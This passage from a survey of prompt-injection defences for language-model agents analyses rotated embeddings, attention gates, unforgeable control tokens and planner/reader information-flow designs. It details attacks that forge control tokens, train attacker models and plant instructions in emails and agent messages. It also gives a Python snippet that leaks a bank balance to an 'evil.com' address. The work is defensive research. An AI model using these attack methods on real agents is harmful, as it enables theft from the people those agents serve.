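Weight-sparse models need 100 to 1,000 times as much computation to train and run as dense models of similar ability, partly because current chips are built to multiply solid blocks of numbers, not scattered ones. Gao and colleagues could not keep the models interpretable beyond tens of millions of nonzero weights, and *Understanding AI from the Inside*, a survey from November 2026, still describes this as an open problem.

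In *Sparse Weight Decomposition for Efficient Circuit Extraction*, Yan, Huang and colleagues (2026) approximate a weight matrix $W$ of an existing model by a product $AB$ of two sparse matrices, rather than training a sparse model from scratch. They replaced all 48 attention and feed-forward matrices of GPT-2 Small and then did some fine-tuning. In models as large as Qwen3.5-27B, they replaced single matrices. This makes studying circuits much more efficient, but a path missing from $AB$ may still exist in $W$.

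Transformer Programs have worked only on small tasks. When Friedman and colleagues doubled the maximum length and vocabulary to 16, accuracy on the hardest task was more than 50 points below a standard transformer's. Training seems to be the main obstacle. On reversal at this size, programs trained from random initializations got about 24% of tokens right. When the researchers set the gates and matching rules by hand and learned the remaining parameters by training, two of three runs reached 99.9%.

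The architecture can also make correct programs very large. Lee and colleagues' hand-written solution to the ranking task needed a lookup table that grows roughly as $N^V$ for inputs of length $N$ with $V$ possible values. For $N=8$ and $V=6$ that is about 262,000 entries, and doubling the length multiplies it by 64. Longer inputs also make checking harder. For double histogram, the solver took about 100 minutes on inputs of seven tokens, including the start marker, and had not finished after eight hours on inputs of eight. The researchers ran all 279,936 of those inputs instead, but inputs with 16 tokens after the start marker would number almost three trillion.

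Long programs are also hard for people to understand. Lee and colleagues studied two ranking programs, each with 96 learned components and more than 2,000 lines of code. They could explain particular wrong answers but did not work out either program's full method. Friedman and colleagues suggest reading such programs as collections of small features that can each be understood separately. This approach has limits. In the ranking errors, the feature that counted the 4s was correct and easy to read, but the mistake came from how the classifier combined it with the other features.

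## Attack tests of models that separate instructions from data

Transformers that can be converted to readable programs are still too small to run an email assistant, so a developer has to start from an ordinary transformer. It has no built-in way to treat the owner's instructions differently from a stranger's email. A token's first vector, called its embedding, is the same no matter who wrote the token, and every layer applies the same weights at every position. The model can infer who wrote a passage only from context, such as the tokens that mark the start of the user's message, and only training teaches it to follow the owner's instructions rather than those in the email.

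The software around the model can usually label each passage with its source. Researchers have used such labels inside the model to mark untrusted tokens or to weaken the attention they receive. A hard mask could make the answer independent of the email, but as the four-position example showed, the model then couldn't summarise the email. If a design lets the model read the email, the email can still affect the answer, and the evidence that the design resists attacks comes from test scores.

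### Rotating the embeddings of data

Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues (2025), in *ASIDE*, give each token a second embedding for use in data. They split the ordinary vector into pairs of numbers and turn each pair by 90 degrees:

$$(x_1,x_2,x_3,x_4,\dots)\mapsto(-x_2,x_1,-x_4,x_3,\dots).$$

The rotated vector is perpendicular to the original, because each pair of coordinates contributes $-x_1x_2+x_2x_1=0$ to their dot product. An attacker can't avoid the rotation, since the software applies it to everything labelled as data.

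Zverev and colleagues added the rotation to six models with 7 to 13 billion parameters and fine-tuned them on about 52,000 ordinary tasks that contained no attacks. For comparison, they fine-tuned standard versions with special tokens around the data and a prompt identifying the instructions and the data. They then placed an unrelated instruction in either the instructions or the data. A model scores well if it follows the unrelated instruction when it appears in the instructions but not when it appears in the data. The rotation raised this score by 12 to 44 percentage points, for example from 45.3% to 71.4% for Qwen3 8B.

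The rotation also reduced the success of prompt injections, though unevenly. On one set of text tasks, the average success rate across the six models fell from 14.7% to 4.9%. On another, where the injected text told the model to print "hacked", it fell from 45.6% to 28.1%. On that test, the rate fell from 33.4% to 9.6% for Mistral 7B but only from 44.3% to 43.7% for Llama 2 7B. General answer quality stayed within three points of the standard versions, but Mistral's score on a separate test of instruction following fell from 45.0% to 25.3%. All the attacks were fixed texts that had not been adapted to the rotation.

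The rotation causes some of this resistance. When Zverev and colleagues gave the injected instruction ordinary embeddings instead of rotated ones, the model followed it almost twice as often. But a network can reverse a rotation exactly, so the email's full content still reaches the later layers. Training seems to have partly reversed the rotation. At the last position of the text, the cosine similarity between the rotated model's vectors and the standard model's started near 0, rose to 0.8 by the eighth layer and ended around 0.7.

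A later paper, *Heads of Security*, which shares three authors with ASIDE, applied the rotation to GPT-OSS-20B, an open reasoning model from OpenAI. Without any attack, the best rotated version completed 9 of 95 tasks on AgentDojo, compared with 60 for the original model. In 79 of the tasks it never successfully used a tool. No injection succeeded on AgentDojo, but this is weak evidence of protection, because a model that usually failed to use its tools would also have trouble following an injected instruction to misuse them.

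### Penalising attention to untrusted text

The design in *Origin Is All You Need* labels each token as coming from the system prompt, the assistant, the user or an untrusted source. It adds a learned vector for the label to the token's embedding, and a learned number to the attention score between two tokens. That number depends on the two tokens' labels and is the same in every layer and head. Training starts with a large penalty $\delta$ wherever the assistant's or user's tokens read untrusted text.

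Let $S_T$ and $S_U$ be the sums of the exponentiated scores for trusted and untrusted text before the penalty. The share of attention that goes to untrusted text is then

$$\frac{e^{-\delta}S_U}{S_T+e^{-\delta}S_U}.$$

If the two sums are equal and $\delta=5$, this share drops from 50% to 0.7%. But the scores depend on what the attacker writes. Text that scores 5 points higher cancels the penalty and brings the share back to 50%.

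The researchers tested four models with 360 million to 8 billion parameters. For Llama 3 8B, the success rate of fixed attacks fell from 32.5% to 0.7% on a test that resembled the training data, and from 17–24% to almost zero on three that did not. Fine-tuning on the same data without the labels worked nearly as well on the first test, but on one of the others, 2.3% of attacks still succeeded against Llama and 17.8% against Mistral 7B.

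They also ran two attacks that used the defended Llama model's weights to search for effective text. The attacks succeeded 1.4% and 1.6% of the time, compared with about 50% for the original model. The rates for the model fine-tuned without labels were 3.2% and 19.7%. Both attacks looked for a single string that would work on many examples, which is harder than finding one for a particular email.

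The penalty provides nearly all the protection against attacks. Setting it to zero in the Llama model after training raised attack success on the first test to 72.0%, more than twice the original model's rate. Training probably did little to make the model itself resist attacks, because the penalty was already hiding them.

How the researchers assigned the labels is a bigger problem. In the training examples, only the injected instruction was labeled untrusted, and the document around it was labeled trusted. Software that could label text this precisely could delete the attack instead. A real assistant would have to label the whole email as untrusted, so the penalty would hide the invoice too. *Origin Is All You Need* acknowledges that the design also suppresses legitimate content labeled untrusted. Its utility test could not measure this loss because it used open-ended requests rather than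 tasks that depend on untrusted documents. On those requests, an AI judge preferred the defended Llama model's answer to the original model's 48.8% of the time.

### Learning a gate for each attention head

*Heads of Security* presents a method, HoS, that lets each attention head treat untrusted text differently. A head that follows instructions can largely ignore the email while another reads its facts. The attention weight on position $j$ becomes

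$$a_j\propto\sigma(g_{c,c_j})\,\exp\!\left(\frac{q\cdot k_j}{\sqrt{d_h}}\right),$$

where $c$ and $c_j$ are the labels of the reading position and of position $j$, $g$ is a number learned for that head and pair of labels, and $\sigma$ squeezes it into the range between 0 and 1. This factor, the gate, can come close to zero but never reaches it. Training adjusts only the gates, which amount to 18,432 numbers in GPT-OSS-20B, and uses examples in which the preferred answer ignores an injected instruction.

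The researchers also tried giving every head the same fixed gate. The table shows the results for GPT-OSS-20B on AgentDojo with fixed attacks. The first column is the weight on untrusted text relative to trusted text.

| Relative weight | Tasks completed under attack (%) | Attacks that succeeded (%) |
|---|---|---|
| 100% (no defence) | 53.6 | 23.8 |
| 24% | 60.8 | 11.1 |
| 9% | 50.8 | 1.5 |
| 4% | 22.6 | Under 0.4 |
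| Learned for each head | 59.6 | 1.1 |

As a uniform gate closes, attacks stop working, but the assistant also becomes unable to do most tasks, because they need information from tool results. Separate gates for each head avoid most of this loss of ability.

The researchers tested HoS against much stronger attackers than those used for ASIDE. In one attack, reinforcement learning trained a second language model to write injections that made a given target call the attacker's tool. In another, GPT-5.6 Sol spent 50 rounds developing an attack specifically against HoS. This attack used the target's weights to find a separate 120-token string for each case. The next table compares attack success rates against HoS and SecAlign, which fine-tunes millions of weights on similar examples. All rates are for the same 100 goals from InjecAgent, a benchmark for agents with tools. For the trained attackers,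 the table lists the best result among all those tried.

| Attack | GPT-OSS-20B | With SecAlign | With HoS |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed text, medium reasoning effort | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Trained attacker, medium effort | 97 | 85 | 10 |
| Trained attacker, low effort | 100 | 82 | 36 |
| Search using the weights | 95 | 100 | 90 |

In the first two rows, the undefended model resisted every fixed injection, but a trained attacker beat it 97% of the time. ASIDE's scores all come from fixed attacks, so they give little indication of how it would do against an attacker who studied it.

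The 10% figure for HoS could also be too low, because it comes from an attacker trained against SecAlign. The attacker trained against HoS at medium effort did worse, probably because too few of its attempts succeeded for it to learn much. When the search used the model's weights, HoS raised the computation needed for a 50% success rate about threefold. With the full budget, the search still found a working string for 90 of the 100 goals.

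HoS preserved most abilities. GPT-OSS-20B scored 67.2% on a hard knowledge test with five worked examples in the prompt, down from 68.3%. Llama 3.3 70B completed slightly more AgentDojo tasks than before when there was no attack, but its completion rate on AgentDyn, another agent benchmark, fell from 33.7% to 18.3%. The gates also made GPT-OSS-20B less likely to report an attack. When asked to summarise emails and flag injected instructions, it flagged 3.1% of the instructions, down from 11.0%.

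### Making control tokens impossible to forge

*Nameless Tokenization* (Yang, Jang and Lim, 2026) offers a much narrower but exact guarantee. Chat models reserve tokens, called control tokens, to mark where a user's message, a system instruction or a tool result begins and ends. Each control token has a written name, and a standard tokenizer (the program that turns text into tokens) converts that name into the control token wherever it appears. An attacker can therefore write an email that includes the name of the token that ends the email, followed by a fake message from the owner.

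Yang and colleagues checked 256 tokenizers for popular open models and could forge control tokens in all of them. A setting that developers often recommend as a fix left 56.6% of the tokenizers vulnerable. The setting blocks only the tokens a developer has marked as special, and many developers had not marked the tokens for tool calls and reasoning.

Their solution uses a second tokenizer for message content, with the control tokens' names removed. The software that assembles the conversation inserts the real control tokens directly by number. If $E(t)$ is the set of tokens the second tokenizer produces from a text $t$, and $C$ is the set of control tokens, then

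$$E(t)\cap C=\varnothing\quad\text{for every text }t.$$

An attacker's text can't produce a control token, no matter how the attacker words it, because the tokenizer has no entry that maps text to one. Anyone with the tokenizer and the software that assembles the input can check this without the model's weights. The guarantee doesn't apply if a caller can submit token numbers instead of text.

The defence left the tokens of ordinary prompts unchanged, and accuracy on three standard tasks was 88.9%, compared with 89.1% before. Whether it stops injections is another matter. Yang and colleagues put the same instruction behind different delimiters and measured how often five models followed it, in per cent:

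| What comes before the injected instruction | Standard tokenizer | Nameless tokenization |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 62.5 | 62.4 |
| Misspelled control tokens | 93.0 | 93.0 |
| A forged user message | 99.9 | 92.8 |
| A forged system message | 46.9 | 68.0 |
| A forged tool result (two models) | 33.1 | 7.4 |

The models mostly responded to text that looked like a boundary, whether or not it contained real control tokens. Forged system messages even worked better as plain text than with real control tokens, perhaps because the plain text stayed inside the user's message, which the model was about to answer.

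The defence helped more when the system prompt told the model to treat the user's message as data. With that warning, Ministral 3 8B ignored every plain injection but still obeyed 99.0% of forged user messages with real control tokens, compared with 23.3% without them. GPT-OSS-20B obeyed nearly all the injections either way. The attacks were fixed texts, but the guarantee about control tokens doesn't depend on which attacks the researchers tried. It doesn't cover text that persuades the model without using control tokens.

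### The inseparability theorem

Pant and colleagues argue that no defence within a shared stream of vectors can prevent prompt injection perfectly. Their theorem concerns control decisions, such as whether to refuse a request, call a tool or write to memory. It requires that rewording an untrusted text without changing its meaning never changes these decisions. Let $s$ be the trusted instructions, $u$ and $u'$ two untrusted texts, and $D$ the distribution over control decisions. The condition is

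$$u\equiv u'\;\Rightarrow\;D(s,u)=D(s,u'),$$

where $u\equiv u'$ means that the two texts have the same meaning for the task. Pant and colleagues call this semantic-faithful control.

The theorem applies to systems that meet three conditions:

- Trusted and untrusted text pass through the same layers and attention.
- Nothing in the architecture enforces a separation that the attacker can't alter.
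- The control decisions come from this shared computation.

It exempts models with separate encoders for trusted and untrusted text, models with hard attention masks, and systems where ordinary software outside the model makes the decisions.

The proof combines three observations. Untrusted text influences the decision through attention. Vectors from trusted and untrusted text overlap, so the model can't always distinguish them by source. Training covers only finitely many of the endless ways to word a message, so correct behaviour on the training data doesn't guarantee correct behaviour on a new wording.

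That much is sound, but the proof then concludes that the condition fails for some new wording, which does not follow. A model that refuses every request can meet all three conditions of the theorem and can still attend to the email, but its decision never changes, so it satisfies semantic-faithful control. The argument also does not rule out proving the property by analysing a finished model's weights, though Wurm's results suggest that would be hard.

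The property is also a poor definition of safety against injection. An assistant satisfies the property if it pays whenever an email asks for money, however the email is worded, because its decision depends only on the email's meaning. Pant and colleagues deliberately allow this dependence because a model should be able to refuse a harmful request based on its meaning. But in the emailed invoice example, the owner needs noninterference or a limit on what the email may influence.

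### Overlapping vectors and ASIDE

Pant and colleagues' first lemma is about the overlap between embeddings, which occurs because both kinds of text share tokens. In their samples, 62% to 82% of the distinct tokens in system prompts also appeared in users' messages.

Their measurements only weakly support the overlap they assume in deeper layers. They measured the distance between the distributions of vectors for system prompts and user messages in Llama 3.1 8B. The distance rose from 0.61 at the embeddings to 0.91 at layer 8, then fell to 0.76 at layer 31. But two distributions can be close together without overlapping, just as two separate points can. They also averaged the vectors over each text, although the theorem concerns the positions where the model makes its decision.

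The first lemma does not apply to ASIDE. An instruction token has the embedding $e$ and the same token in data has $Re$, where $R$ is the rotation. The two are at right angles, so they differ unless $e$ is zero. The sets could still overlap if one token's rotated embedding equaled another token's ordinary one, but this is very unlikely with thousands of dimensions. Anyone with the embedding table can check. Zverev and colleagues found that a simple classifier could identify the source of every vector at the first layer, as expected if the sets don't overlap.

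ASIDE gives the network a reliable signal of where each token came from, but nothing forces the network to act on that signal. The email still reaches the decision through attention, and the model still learns from finitely many examples what to do with it. Pant and colleagues therefore overstate what ASIDE does when they describe it as "exactly the non-forgeable, architecture-level separation our result requires". The theorem exempts designs that enforce separation by construction, which neither ASIDE nor the labels in *Origin Is All You Need* and HoS do.

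### No guarantee and no resistance

Bhattarai and Vu's theorem on separating commands from data by content alone supports the same conclusion. It applies only to systems in which no trusted component checks a record of where text came from. They state that in such systems, some text from an attacker will make the model treat data as a command "with non-zero probability".

This conclusion is weaker than it sounds, because a model that samples its words usually gives every possible output some probability, so it could make a forbidden tool call even after a harmless email. The theorem doesn't distinguish a chance of one in two from one in a billion. It also doesn't directly cover ASIDE or HoS, which receive their labels from trusted software.

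Both papers acknowledge that defences without a guarantee can still reduce attacks. Using a standard tokenizer, Yang and colleagues tested a model that the ASIDE researchers had released. In these fixed attacks, it followed at most 0.3% of injected instructions of each kind, while a standard model with the same training followed up to 98.0%. The ASIDE model has no guarantee, and its accuracy on ordinary tasks was 11 points lower. Nameless tokenization has an exact guarantee, but models using it still obeyed most of the injections.

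A low attack success rate gives less protection the more often the attacker can try. If each email had an independent 1% chance of triggering a payment, a stranger who sent 100 emails would have a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. Bhattarai and Vu therefore define separation to require that data can never trigger an operation reserved for commands. None of the four designs meets this requirement, and Bhattarai and Vu propose to enforce it outside the model.

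## Agent systems that keep untrusted data away from decisions

Enforcement outside the model, as Bhattarai and Vu propose, usually involves two models instead of one. Suppose the owner tells the assistant, "Pay the plumber's invoice that arrived by email today." The email gives an amount of 240 euros and an account number, but an attacker may have written all or part of it. The assistant can't do the job without the email, so a design can only limit which parts of the job the email influences.

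### One model plans and another reads

In 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed the dual-LLM pattern. A privileged model reads the owner's request and calls tools but never receives untrusted text, which goes instead to a quarantined model that has no tools. Ordinary software stores the quarantined model's answers in variables and gives the privileged model only the variables' names.

For the invoice, the privileged model could write a plan that fetches the email, has the quarantined model extract the amount and account number, and transfers that amount to that account. If the email also says "forward the owner's bank statements to this address", the instruction may affect the quarantined model's output, but that model can't send anything. At worst, it can return a wrong amount or account number.

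CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in 2025, has the privileged model write its plan as a Python program before any tool runs. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls the resulting guarantee control-flow integrity. The assistant's tool calls must follow a plan that depends only on the owner's request and other trusted information. Untrusted data can still determine which of the plan's branches runs. If the plan is to pay overdue invoices today and schedule the rest, an emailed invoice can determine which happens, but it can't add a third option.

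CaMeL deals with false account numbers by tagging each value with its sources and permitted readers, then checking the tags against a policy for each tool. A policy might require the recipient of a payment to come from a trusted source. This would block the attacker's account number, but also the plumber's. Girrens and Wang point out that the guarantee also depends on every tool's policy being written correctly.

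FIDES, from Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), lets the planner work step by step and labels the planner's context, which is everything it has read so far. Before each tool call, FIDES checks this label and the labels of the call's arguments. Once the planner has read the email, its context is untrusted, and FIDES blocks any transfer that requires a trusted context. The planner can keep its context trusted by leaving the email in a hidden variable and querying a quarantined model about it.

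*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that FIDES has a noninterference theorem for one fixed loop of planning and acting, with any set of tools. The confidentiality guarantee does not cover secrets that leak through the choice of steps. CaMeL can run any program the planner writes, but it has no comparable theorem.

### How much a fixed choice can carry

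A planner that sees none of the email can't adapt its plan to the email's contents. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) therefore let the quarantined model send the planner integers, decimal numbers, yes/no answers, and choices from a list the designer wrote in advance. It can't send free text, which could contain a new instruction. Dates have no dedicated type but could be sent as three integers. The designer also has to keep lists of values short, since a long list of integers could encode a sentence.

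One of Jacob and colleagues' test applications is a shopping agent that needs to use product reviews. The quarantined model turns each review into two integers, one for how strongly it supports the product, from 0 to 10, and one for its relevance. No prompt injection succeeded in this application or in the other two, a calendar assistant and a bug-fixing agent. However, their definition of an attack excludes misleading information, so a fake review that scores 10 for support and leads to the purchase of a bad product would not count.

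A value with $n$ possible settings can carry at most $\log_2 n$ bits. A yes/no answer carries at most one bit and a choice among eight at most three. Successive answers add up:

$$\log_2(n_1n_2\cdots n_k)=\log_2 n_1+\log_2 n_2+\dots+\log_2 n_k.$$

Ten choices among eight options each can carry 30 bits, enough to pick out one of about a billion messages. A ten-digit account number carries about 33 bits. A design that passes account numbers to the planner as integers would also pass an attacker's account number.

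The number of bits limits how many different outcomes the email can cause, but not how bad the worst one is. If the quarantined model answers the question "Is this invoice genuine?", an attacker needs only one bit to get a fake invoice paid. The possible harm depends more on which options are on the list. If the eight options are the owner's regular suppliers, a false email can send money to the wrong supplier but not to a stranger.

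A short list also makes testing easier. If the owner's request and all randomness are fixed, a single choice among eight values can lead to at most eight different runs. A tester can try all eight without inventing any malicious emails. Ten such choices would produce too many combinations to try.

### A secret that leaks through a skipped step

These designs work only if the software tracks every flow, and some flows are easy to miss. Garby and colleagues found one in CaMeL that involves confidentiality. Suppose outsiders must not learn the owner's bank balance. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email if the balance exceeds a threshold, because whether it sends the email depends on a secret. But a program like this one gets past the check:

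```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program assigns to it under a secret condition. The table shows the values and labels just before the last step.

| | Balance above threshold | Balance not above threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp` | False, secret | True, public |
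| `rich` | True, public | False, public |
| Email | Sent | Not sent |

When the balance is high, the program skips the line `rich = False` because of a secret. CaMeL labels only the assignments that the program executes, so `rich` stays public. When the balance is low, `tmp` never becomes secret, and the program sets `rich` to false under a public condition. In both cases `rich` is public, and its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. Denning described this kind of flow in 1976.

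An email can't insert this program into CaMeL's plan, because the planner doesn't read the email. The planner would have to write it by mistake or under some other influence. But the example shows that no confidentiality theorem can hold for every program CaMeL accepts.

Garby and colleagues found another leak outside the part of CaMeL that tracks labels. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop has the planner try again. Whether CaMeL blocked the program can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. If each attempt tested which half of the remaining range contained the balance, 20 attempts could find any whole-euro balance up to about one million euros.

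### Labels on every value

To close such gaps, Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions. Every value has a label, which in the basic version can contain two marks, U for untrusted and S for secret. A value computed from others gets all their marks. The interpreter (the program that runs LLMbda code) also keeps a label for the current point in the program, which records what influenced the decision to run that step. Whatever the step produces gets those marks too.

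The conversation with the language model has a label that combines the labels of all its messages. If the model replies with code, the interpreter runs it under the conversation's label. If the program puts the emailed invoice into its main conversation, every later reply carries the mark U, and a payment tool that requires a trusted recipient will reject an account number from any of those replies.

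Two commands help a program avoid this. `fork` runs a step in a temporary copy of the conversation and then discards the copy, and `clear` empties the current conversation. To create a quarantined reader, a program forks the conversation, clears the copy and runs its query there. The answer still carries the mark U, but the main conversation remains trusted. Programmers can therefore write the dual-LLM pattern in LLMbda themselves instead of relying on an architecture that fixes it in place.

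LLMbda also guards against leaks through steps that a program skips. In one example, a program sends the model the message "Set x = true" only if a secret is true. The interpreter stops the program before it can send the message, because marking the conversation as secret when the message is sent would not be enough. If the secret were false, the program would skip the message, the conversation would stay public, and the model's later answer would reveal the secret.

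### The noninterference theorem

Stopping can itself reveal something, so the theorem that Garby and colleagues prove has to allow for it. Take two runs that differ only in data hidden from an observer. To protect integrity, this hidden data is the email, and the observer sees only values without the mark U. Let $\mu(q)$ and $\nu(q)$ be the probabilities of outcome $q$ in the two runs, as far as the observer can distinguish outcomes. These probabilities may add up to less than one, because a run may stop with an error or never finish. The theorem requires that some third distribution, also with a total of at most one, be at least as large as both for every outcome. This is equivalent to

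$$\sum_q\max(\mu(q),\nu(q))\le 1.$$

If both runs always finish, this condition forces $\mu$ and $\nu$ to be equal, as in exact noninterference. Otherwise, let $d_\mu$ and $d_\nu$ be the probabilities that the runs don't finish. The difference between the runs then has the limit

$$\tfrac12\sum_q|\mu(q)-\nu(q)|\le\tfrac12(d_\mu+d_\nu).$$

Suppose that with an honest email, the program produces outcomes A and B with probability 0.5 each. A malicious email could leave A at 0.5, reduce B to 0.3 and make the program fail with probability 0.2, because the larger probabilities for A and B, 0.5 and 0.5, add up to 1. It couldn't change the probabilities to 0.7 and 0.3, because the larger ones would then add up to 1.2. So if the program always finishes when the email is honest, a malicious email can make a payment less likely but not more likely. If the program sometimes fails when the email is honest,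 the theorem allows a malicious email to turn those failures into payments.

The proof compares both runs with a simplified run, which replaces a step with an empty value as soon as its label exceeds what the observer may see. The simplified run is the same for both emails and finishes at least as often as either original run. Its distribution is therefore at least as large as both $\mu$ and $\nu$, as the theorem requires.

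Lean checked the proof, which covers every LLMbda program, including programs that run code written by a language model. The proof holds whatever the model replies. The interpreter is also written in Lean, and the theorems apply to the code that runs the agent. Developers still have to label their data sources correctly and put the right checks in their tools. The theorem covers only one run at a time, so an outer retry loop could leak a secret bit by bit, as in CaMeL.

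### Endorsement in practice

With these rules alone, the assistant could never pay the plumber through a tool that requires a trusted recipient, because the account number comes from an email. LLMbda therefore has an `endorse` command that removes the mark U from a value. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsements can't cause a secret to leak, but there is no such guarantee for integrity, because endorsement is meant to let untrusted data through.

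An attacker can't remove the untrusted label from data just by sending code that contains the endorsement command, because code generated from an untrusted conversation runs under an untrusted label, and everything it endorses keeps that label. The protection fails if an earlier endorsement has already removed the label from the attacker's text. A stricter version of the command permanently marks every endorsed value and stops the program if it tries to endorse a marked value.

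Another version accepts only values on a fixed list. It endorses a copy of the untrusted value, compares the copy with the list, and releases the copy only if it matches. If it compared the value before endorsing a copy, the result of the comparison would be untrusted, and an endorsement that depended on that result would have no effect. This version works for suppliers the owner already knows but not for a new account number.

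### The banking tests

Garby and colleagues used LLMbda to build an agent called Randori, which writes its final plan before it sees any real data. Randori first tries out the plan on made-up data and corrects any errors there, because correcting the plan during the real task would bring untrusted error messages into the planner's conversation. Garby and colleagues tested Randori on the banking part of AgentDojo, which has 16 tasks and nine injections for each. They ran every combination three times with each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs.

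The table shows the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack.

| System | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0 | 75.0 | 64.6 |
| Randori without endorsement | – | 62.5 | 54.2 |
| CaMeL without policy checks | 66.7 | – | 70.8 |
| CaMeL with policy checks | 37.5 | – | 37.5 |

The policy checks roughly halved the number of tasks CaMeL completed. With only 16 different tasks, the margins of error are 19 to 27 percentage points, so Randori's scores are not distinguishable from those of CaMeL run without policy checks.

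Other systems show a similar drop in completed tasks. Garby and colleagues cite TypeGuard, which enforces comparable rules in Haskell. With its policies turned on, TypeGuard completed 8 of the 21 tasks in AgentDojo's Slack suite, down from 15. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions.

Randori's advantage over CaMeL with policy checks comes partly from looser rules. It implements only some of CaMeL's policies, and its planner may endorse data. For example, Randori's tool for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. An email could therefore determine who receives a scheduled payment, even without an endorsement, and the theorem would still hold.

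Only two of the 1,296 attacks succeeded, but most of the failed attacks are weak evidence that the labels work. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and injection, the attack needed a tool call or file that the plan would never include, so planning before reading was generally enough to stop it. The labels could make a difference only in the other 47 combinations, which account for 423 runs.

Both successful attacks involved the same task and injection. The owner asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The planner had endorsed data from the file before anyone read it, because the task required this. The theorem still held, since it doesn't guarantee integrity once a plan endorses untrusted data. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack, but it would also have to refuse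 a legitimate bill. To stop only the attack, it would have to judge whether the file looked suspicious, which it can't do from labels.

Without its policy checks, CaMeL failed in a different way on a task that told the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it precisely. The planner wrote a program with a branch for each tool, and the file's contents determined which branch ran. The agent never departed from the plan, so control-flow integrity held, but the attacker could choose what the agent did. Girrens and Wang's system SPA also failed on this task with its label checks off, and the four attacks that succeeded against it on AgentDojo in that setting were all on this task.

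### Memory between requests

If an invoice is stored on Monday and paid on Tuesday, a planner that read the stored text would also read any command in it. SPA's planner therefore sees only a description of each stored item: its format, its purpose and the request that produced it. The planner wrote the purpose before any tool opened the invoice, so an attacker couldn't influence it. SPA keeps the stored value's label and retrieves the value only when the new plan runs.

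To test this, Girrens and Wang split each of AgentDojo's 97 tasks into two to five requests. With label checks off, later plans retrieved an available stored item 95.4% of the time, and SPA completed 62.5% of tasks. Letting the planner read the stored values raised the completion rate only to 65.9%, so hiding them made little difference. Turning on the label checks lowered the completion rate to 35.3%, because SPA then rejected about 45% of plans.

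Attacks succeeded in at most 0.6% of runs in any configuration, but Girrens and Wang acknowledge that their attack hardly tests delayed injections. At least two of the attacks that succeeded with label checks on occurred in runs where SPA had already rejected the plan.

SPA allows only one plan per request, and if the check rejects that plan, the request fails. This stops the planner from repeatedly revising an unsafe plan to get it past the check, but also from correcting an accidental error.

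### Recovering from a blocked action

An agent that plans step by step can change its approach, but its label only gets more restrictive. After it reads one email, its context stays untrusted, and every later transfer that requires a trusted context fails. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that gives the agent ways to recover. The agent can read the email in a temporary branch, which keeps the email out of the main context and returns only fields of a fixed form, such as an invoice number and a category.

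When APPA blocks an action, it returns the condition that would make the action permissible, such as a manager's approval. The approval applies only to that exact call and expires after one use. APPA also checks what the context's label would be after the call, so it can block a tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it in a single step, which a check of the current label would miss.

Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA on 20 multi-step office tasks, and it completed 88% of runs with GPT-5.6 Luna. This dropped to 56.5% without temporary branches and to 35.0% without the suggested remedies. No attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs across this benchmark and another. Two versions of FIDES that the team set up completed 36–46% of the office runs, and 26–35% of runs ended in a successful attack. These figures are weak evidence about FIDES itself, because its policies in these tests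 left out several rules that the tasks depended on.

They did not use AgentDojo because frontier models resisted its injections without any defence. But *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) found that Gemini 2.5 Flash followed 41.5% of them. The trained attackers in *Heads of Security* also beat a model that had resisted every fixed injection. A low attack success rate on AgentDojo therefore says little about a defence unless the rate is much higher without it.

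A branch that has read a malicious invoice can return a false value even though its answer has a fixed form. The company that runs the system has to decide whether to treat such values as trusted, so APPA depends on the same kind of judgement as endorsement in LLMbda.

### Tasks too long to plan

Some tasks require too much exploration for a complete plan or a fixed set of fields to be practical. Hu and colleagues used SWE-bench, a benchmark in which agents fix real software bugs based on users' reports. The reports could contain injections, but a privileged model that can't see the reports lacks the information needed to fix the bugs. A strict dual-LLM agent, in which the quarantined model sends no messages to the privileged one, fixed none of them.

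In Twin Agent, an Explore Agent reads everything and writes a short hint before each action. A Safe Agent carries out the actions without seeing the bug report. With hints of up to 100 characters, the system fixed 62.5% of the bugs, compared with 61.2% for an undefended agent. Static injections succeeded against the undefended agent 97.0% of the time but never against Twin Agent. The protection roughly doubled the cost.

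Twin Agent, with hints of up to 200 characters, completed 62.9% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 30.9% for CaMeL. Hu and colleagues had reduced CaMeL's retries from ten to three, and the original CaMeL paper reported about 35%.

Twin Agent has no formal guarantee. A 100-character hint drawn from 95 printable characters can carry $100\log_2 95\approx 657$ bits, compared with three bits for a choice among eight options. The design relies on the assumption that such a short text can't both get past a detector and take control of the Safe Agent.

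Hu and colleagues tested this assumption by optimising malicious hints and adding text to the bug reports telling the Explore Agent to copy the hints. It always did so in single-step tests. In the full test, the detector let a malicious hint through in 57 of 232 tasks, and the Safe Agent carried out the attack in 11 of those, or 4.7% of all tasks. None of the 11 attacks succeeded again in five more attempts each, so success seems to depend partly on chance, but an attacker can also try more than once. In the invoice case, an attacker might not need to take control of the Safe Agent, since a hint can include a false account number and a plausible reason to use it.

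### Agents that instruct other agents

Peters-Gill and colleagues show that a system can be unsafe even if CaMeL protects every agent in it. Suppose a coordinator asks a mail agent for an invoice, then sends a payment agent the message "Pay this invoice" with the invoice text below it. The coordinator's planner never reads the invoice. But the payment agent treats the coordinator as its user, so its own planner reads the whole message as a trusted request, including any command in the invoice.

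In a demonstration of this, the agents were asked to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. Someone had planted an instruction in the applicant database, and the coordinator passed it on inside the summary. The last agent also emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. The first two agents followed exactly the same plans as they did without the attack.

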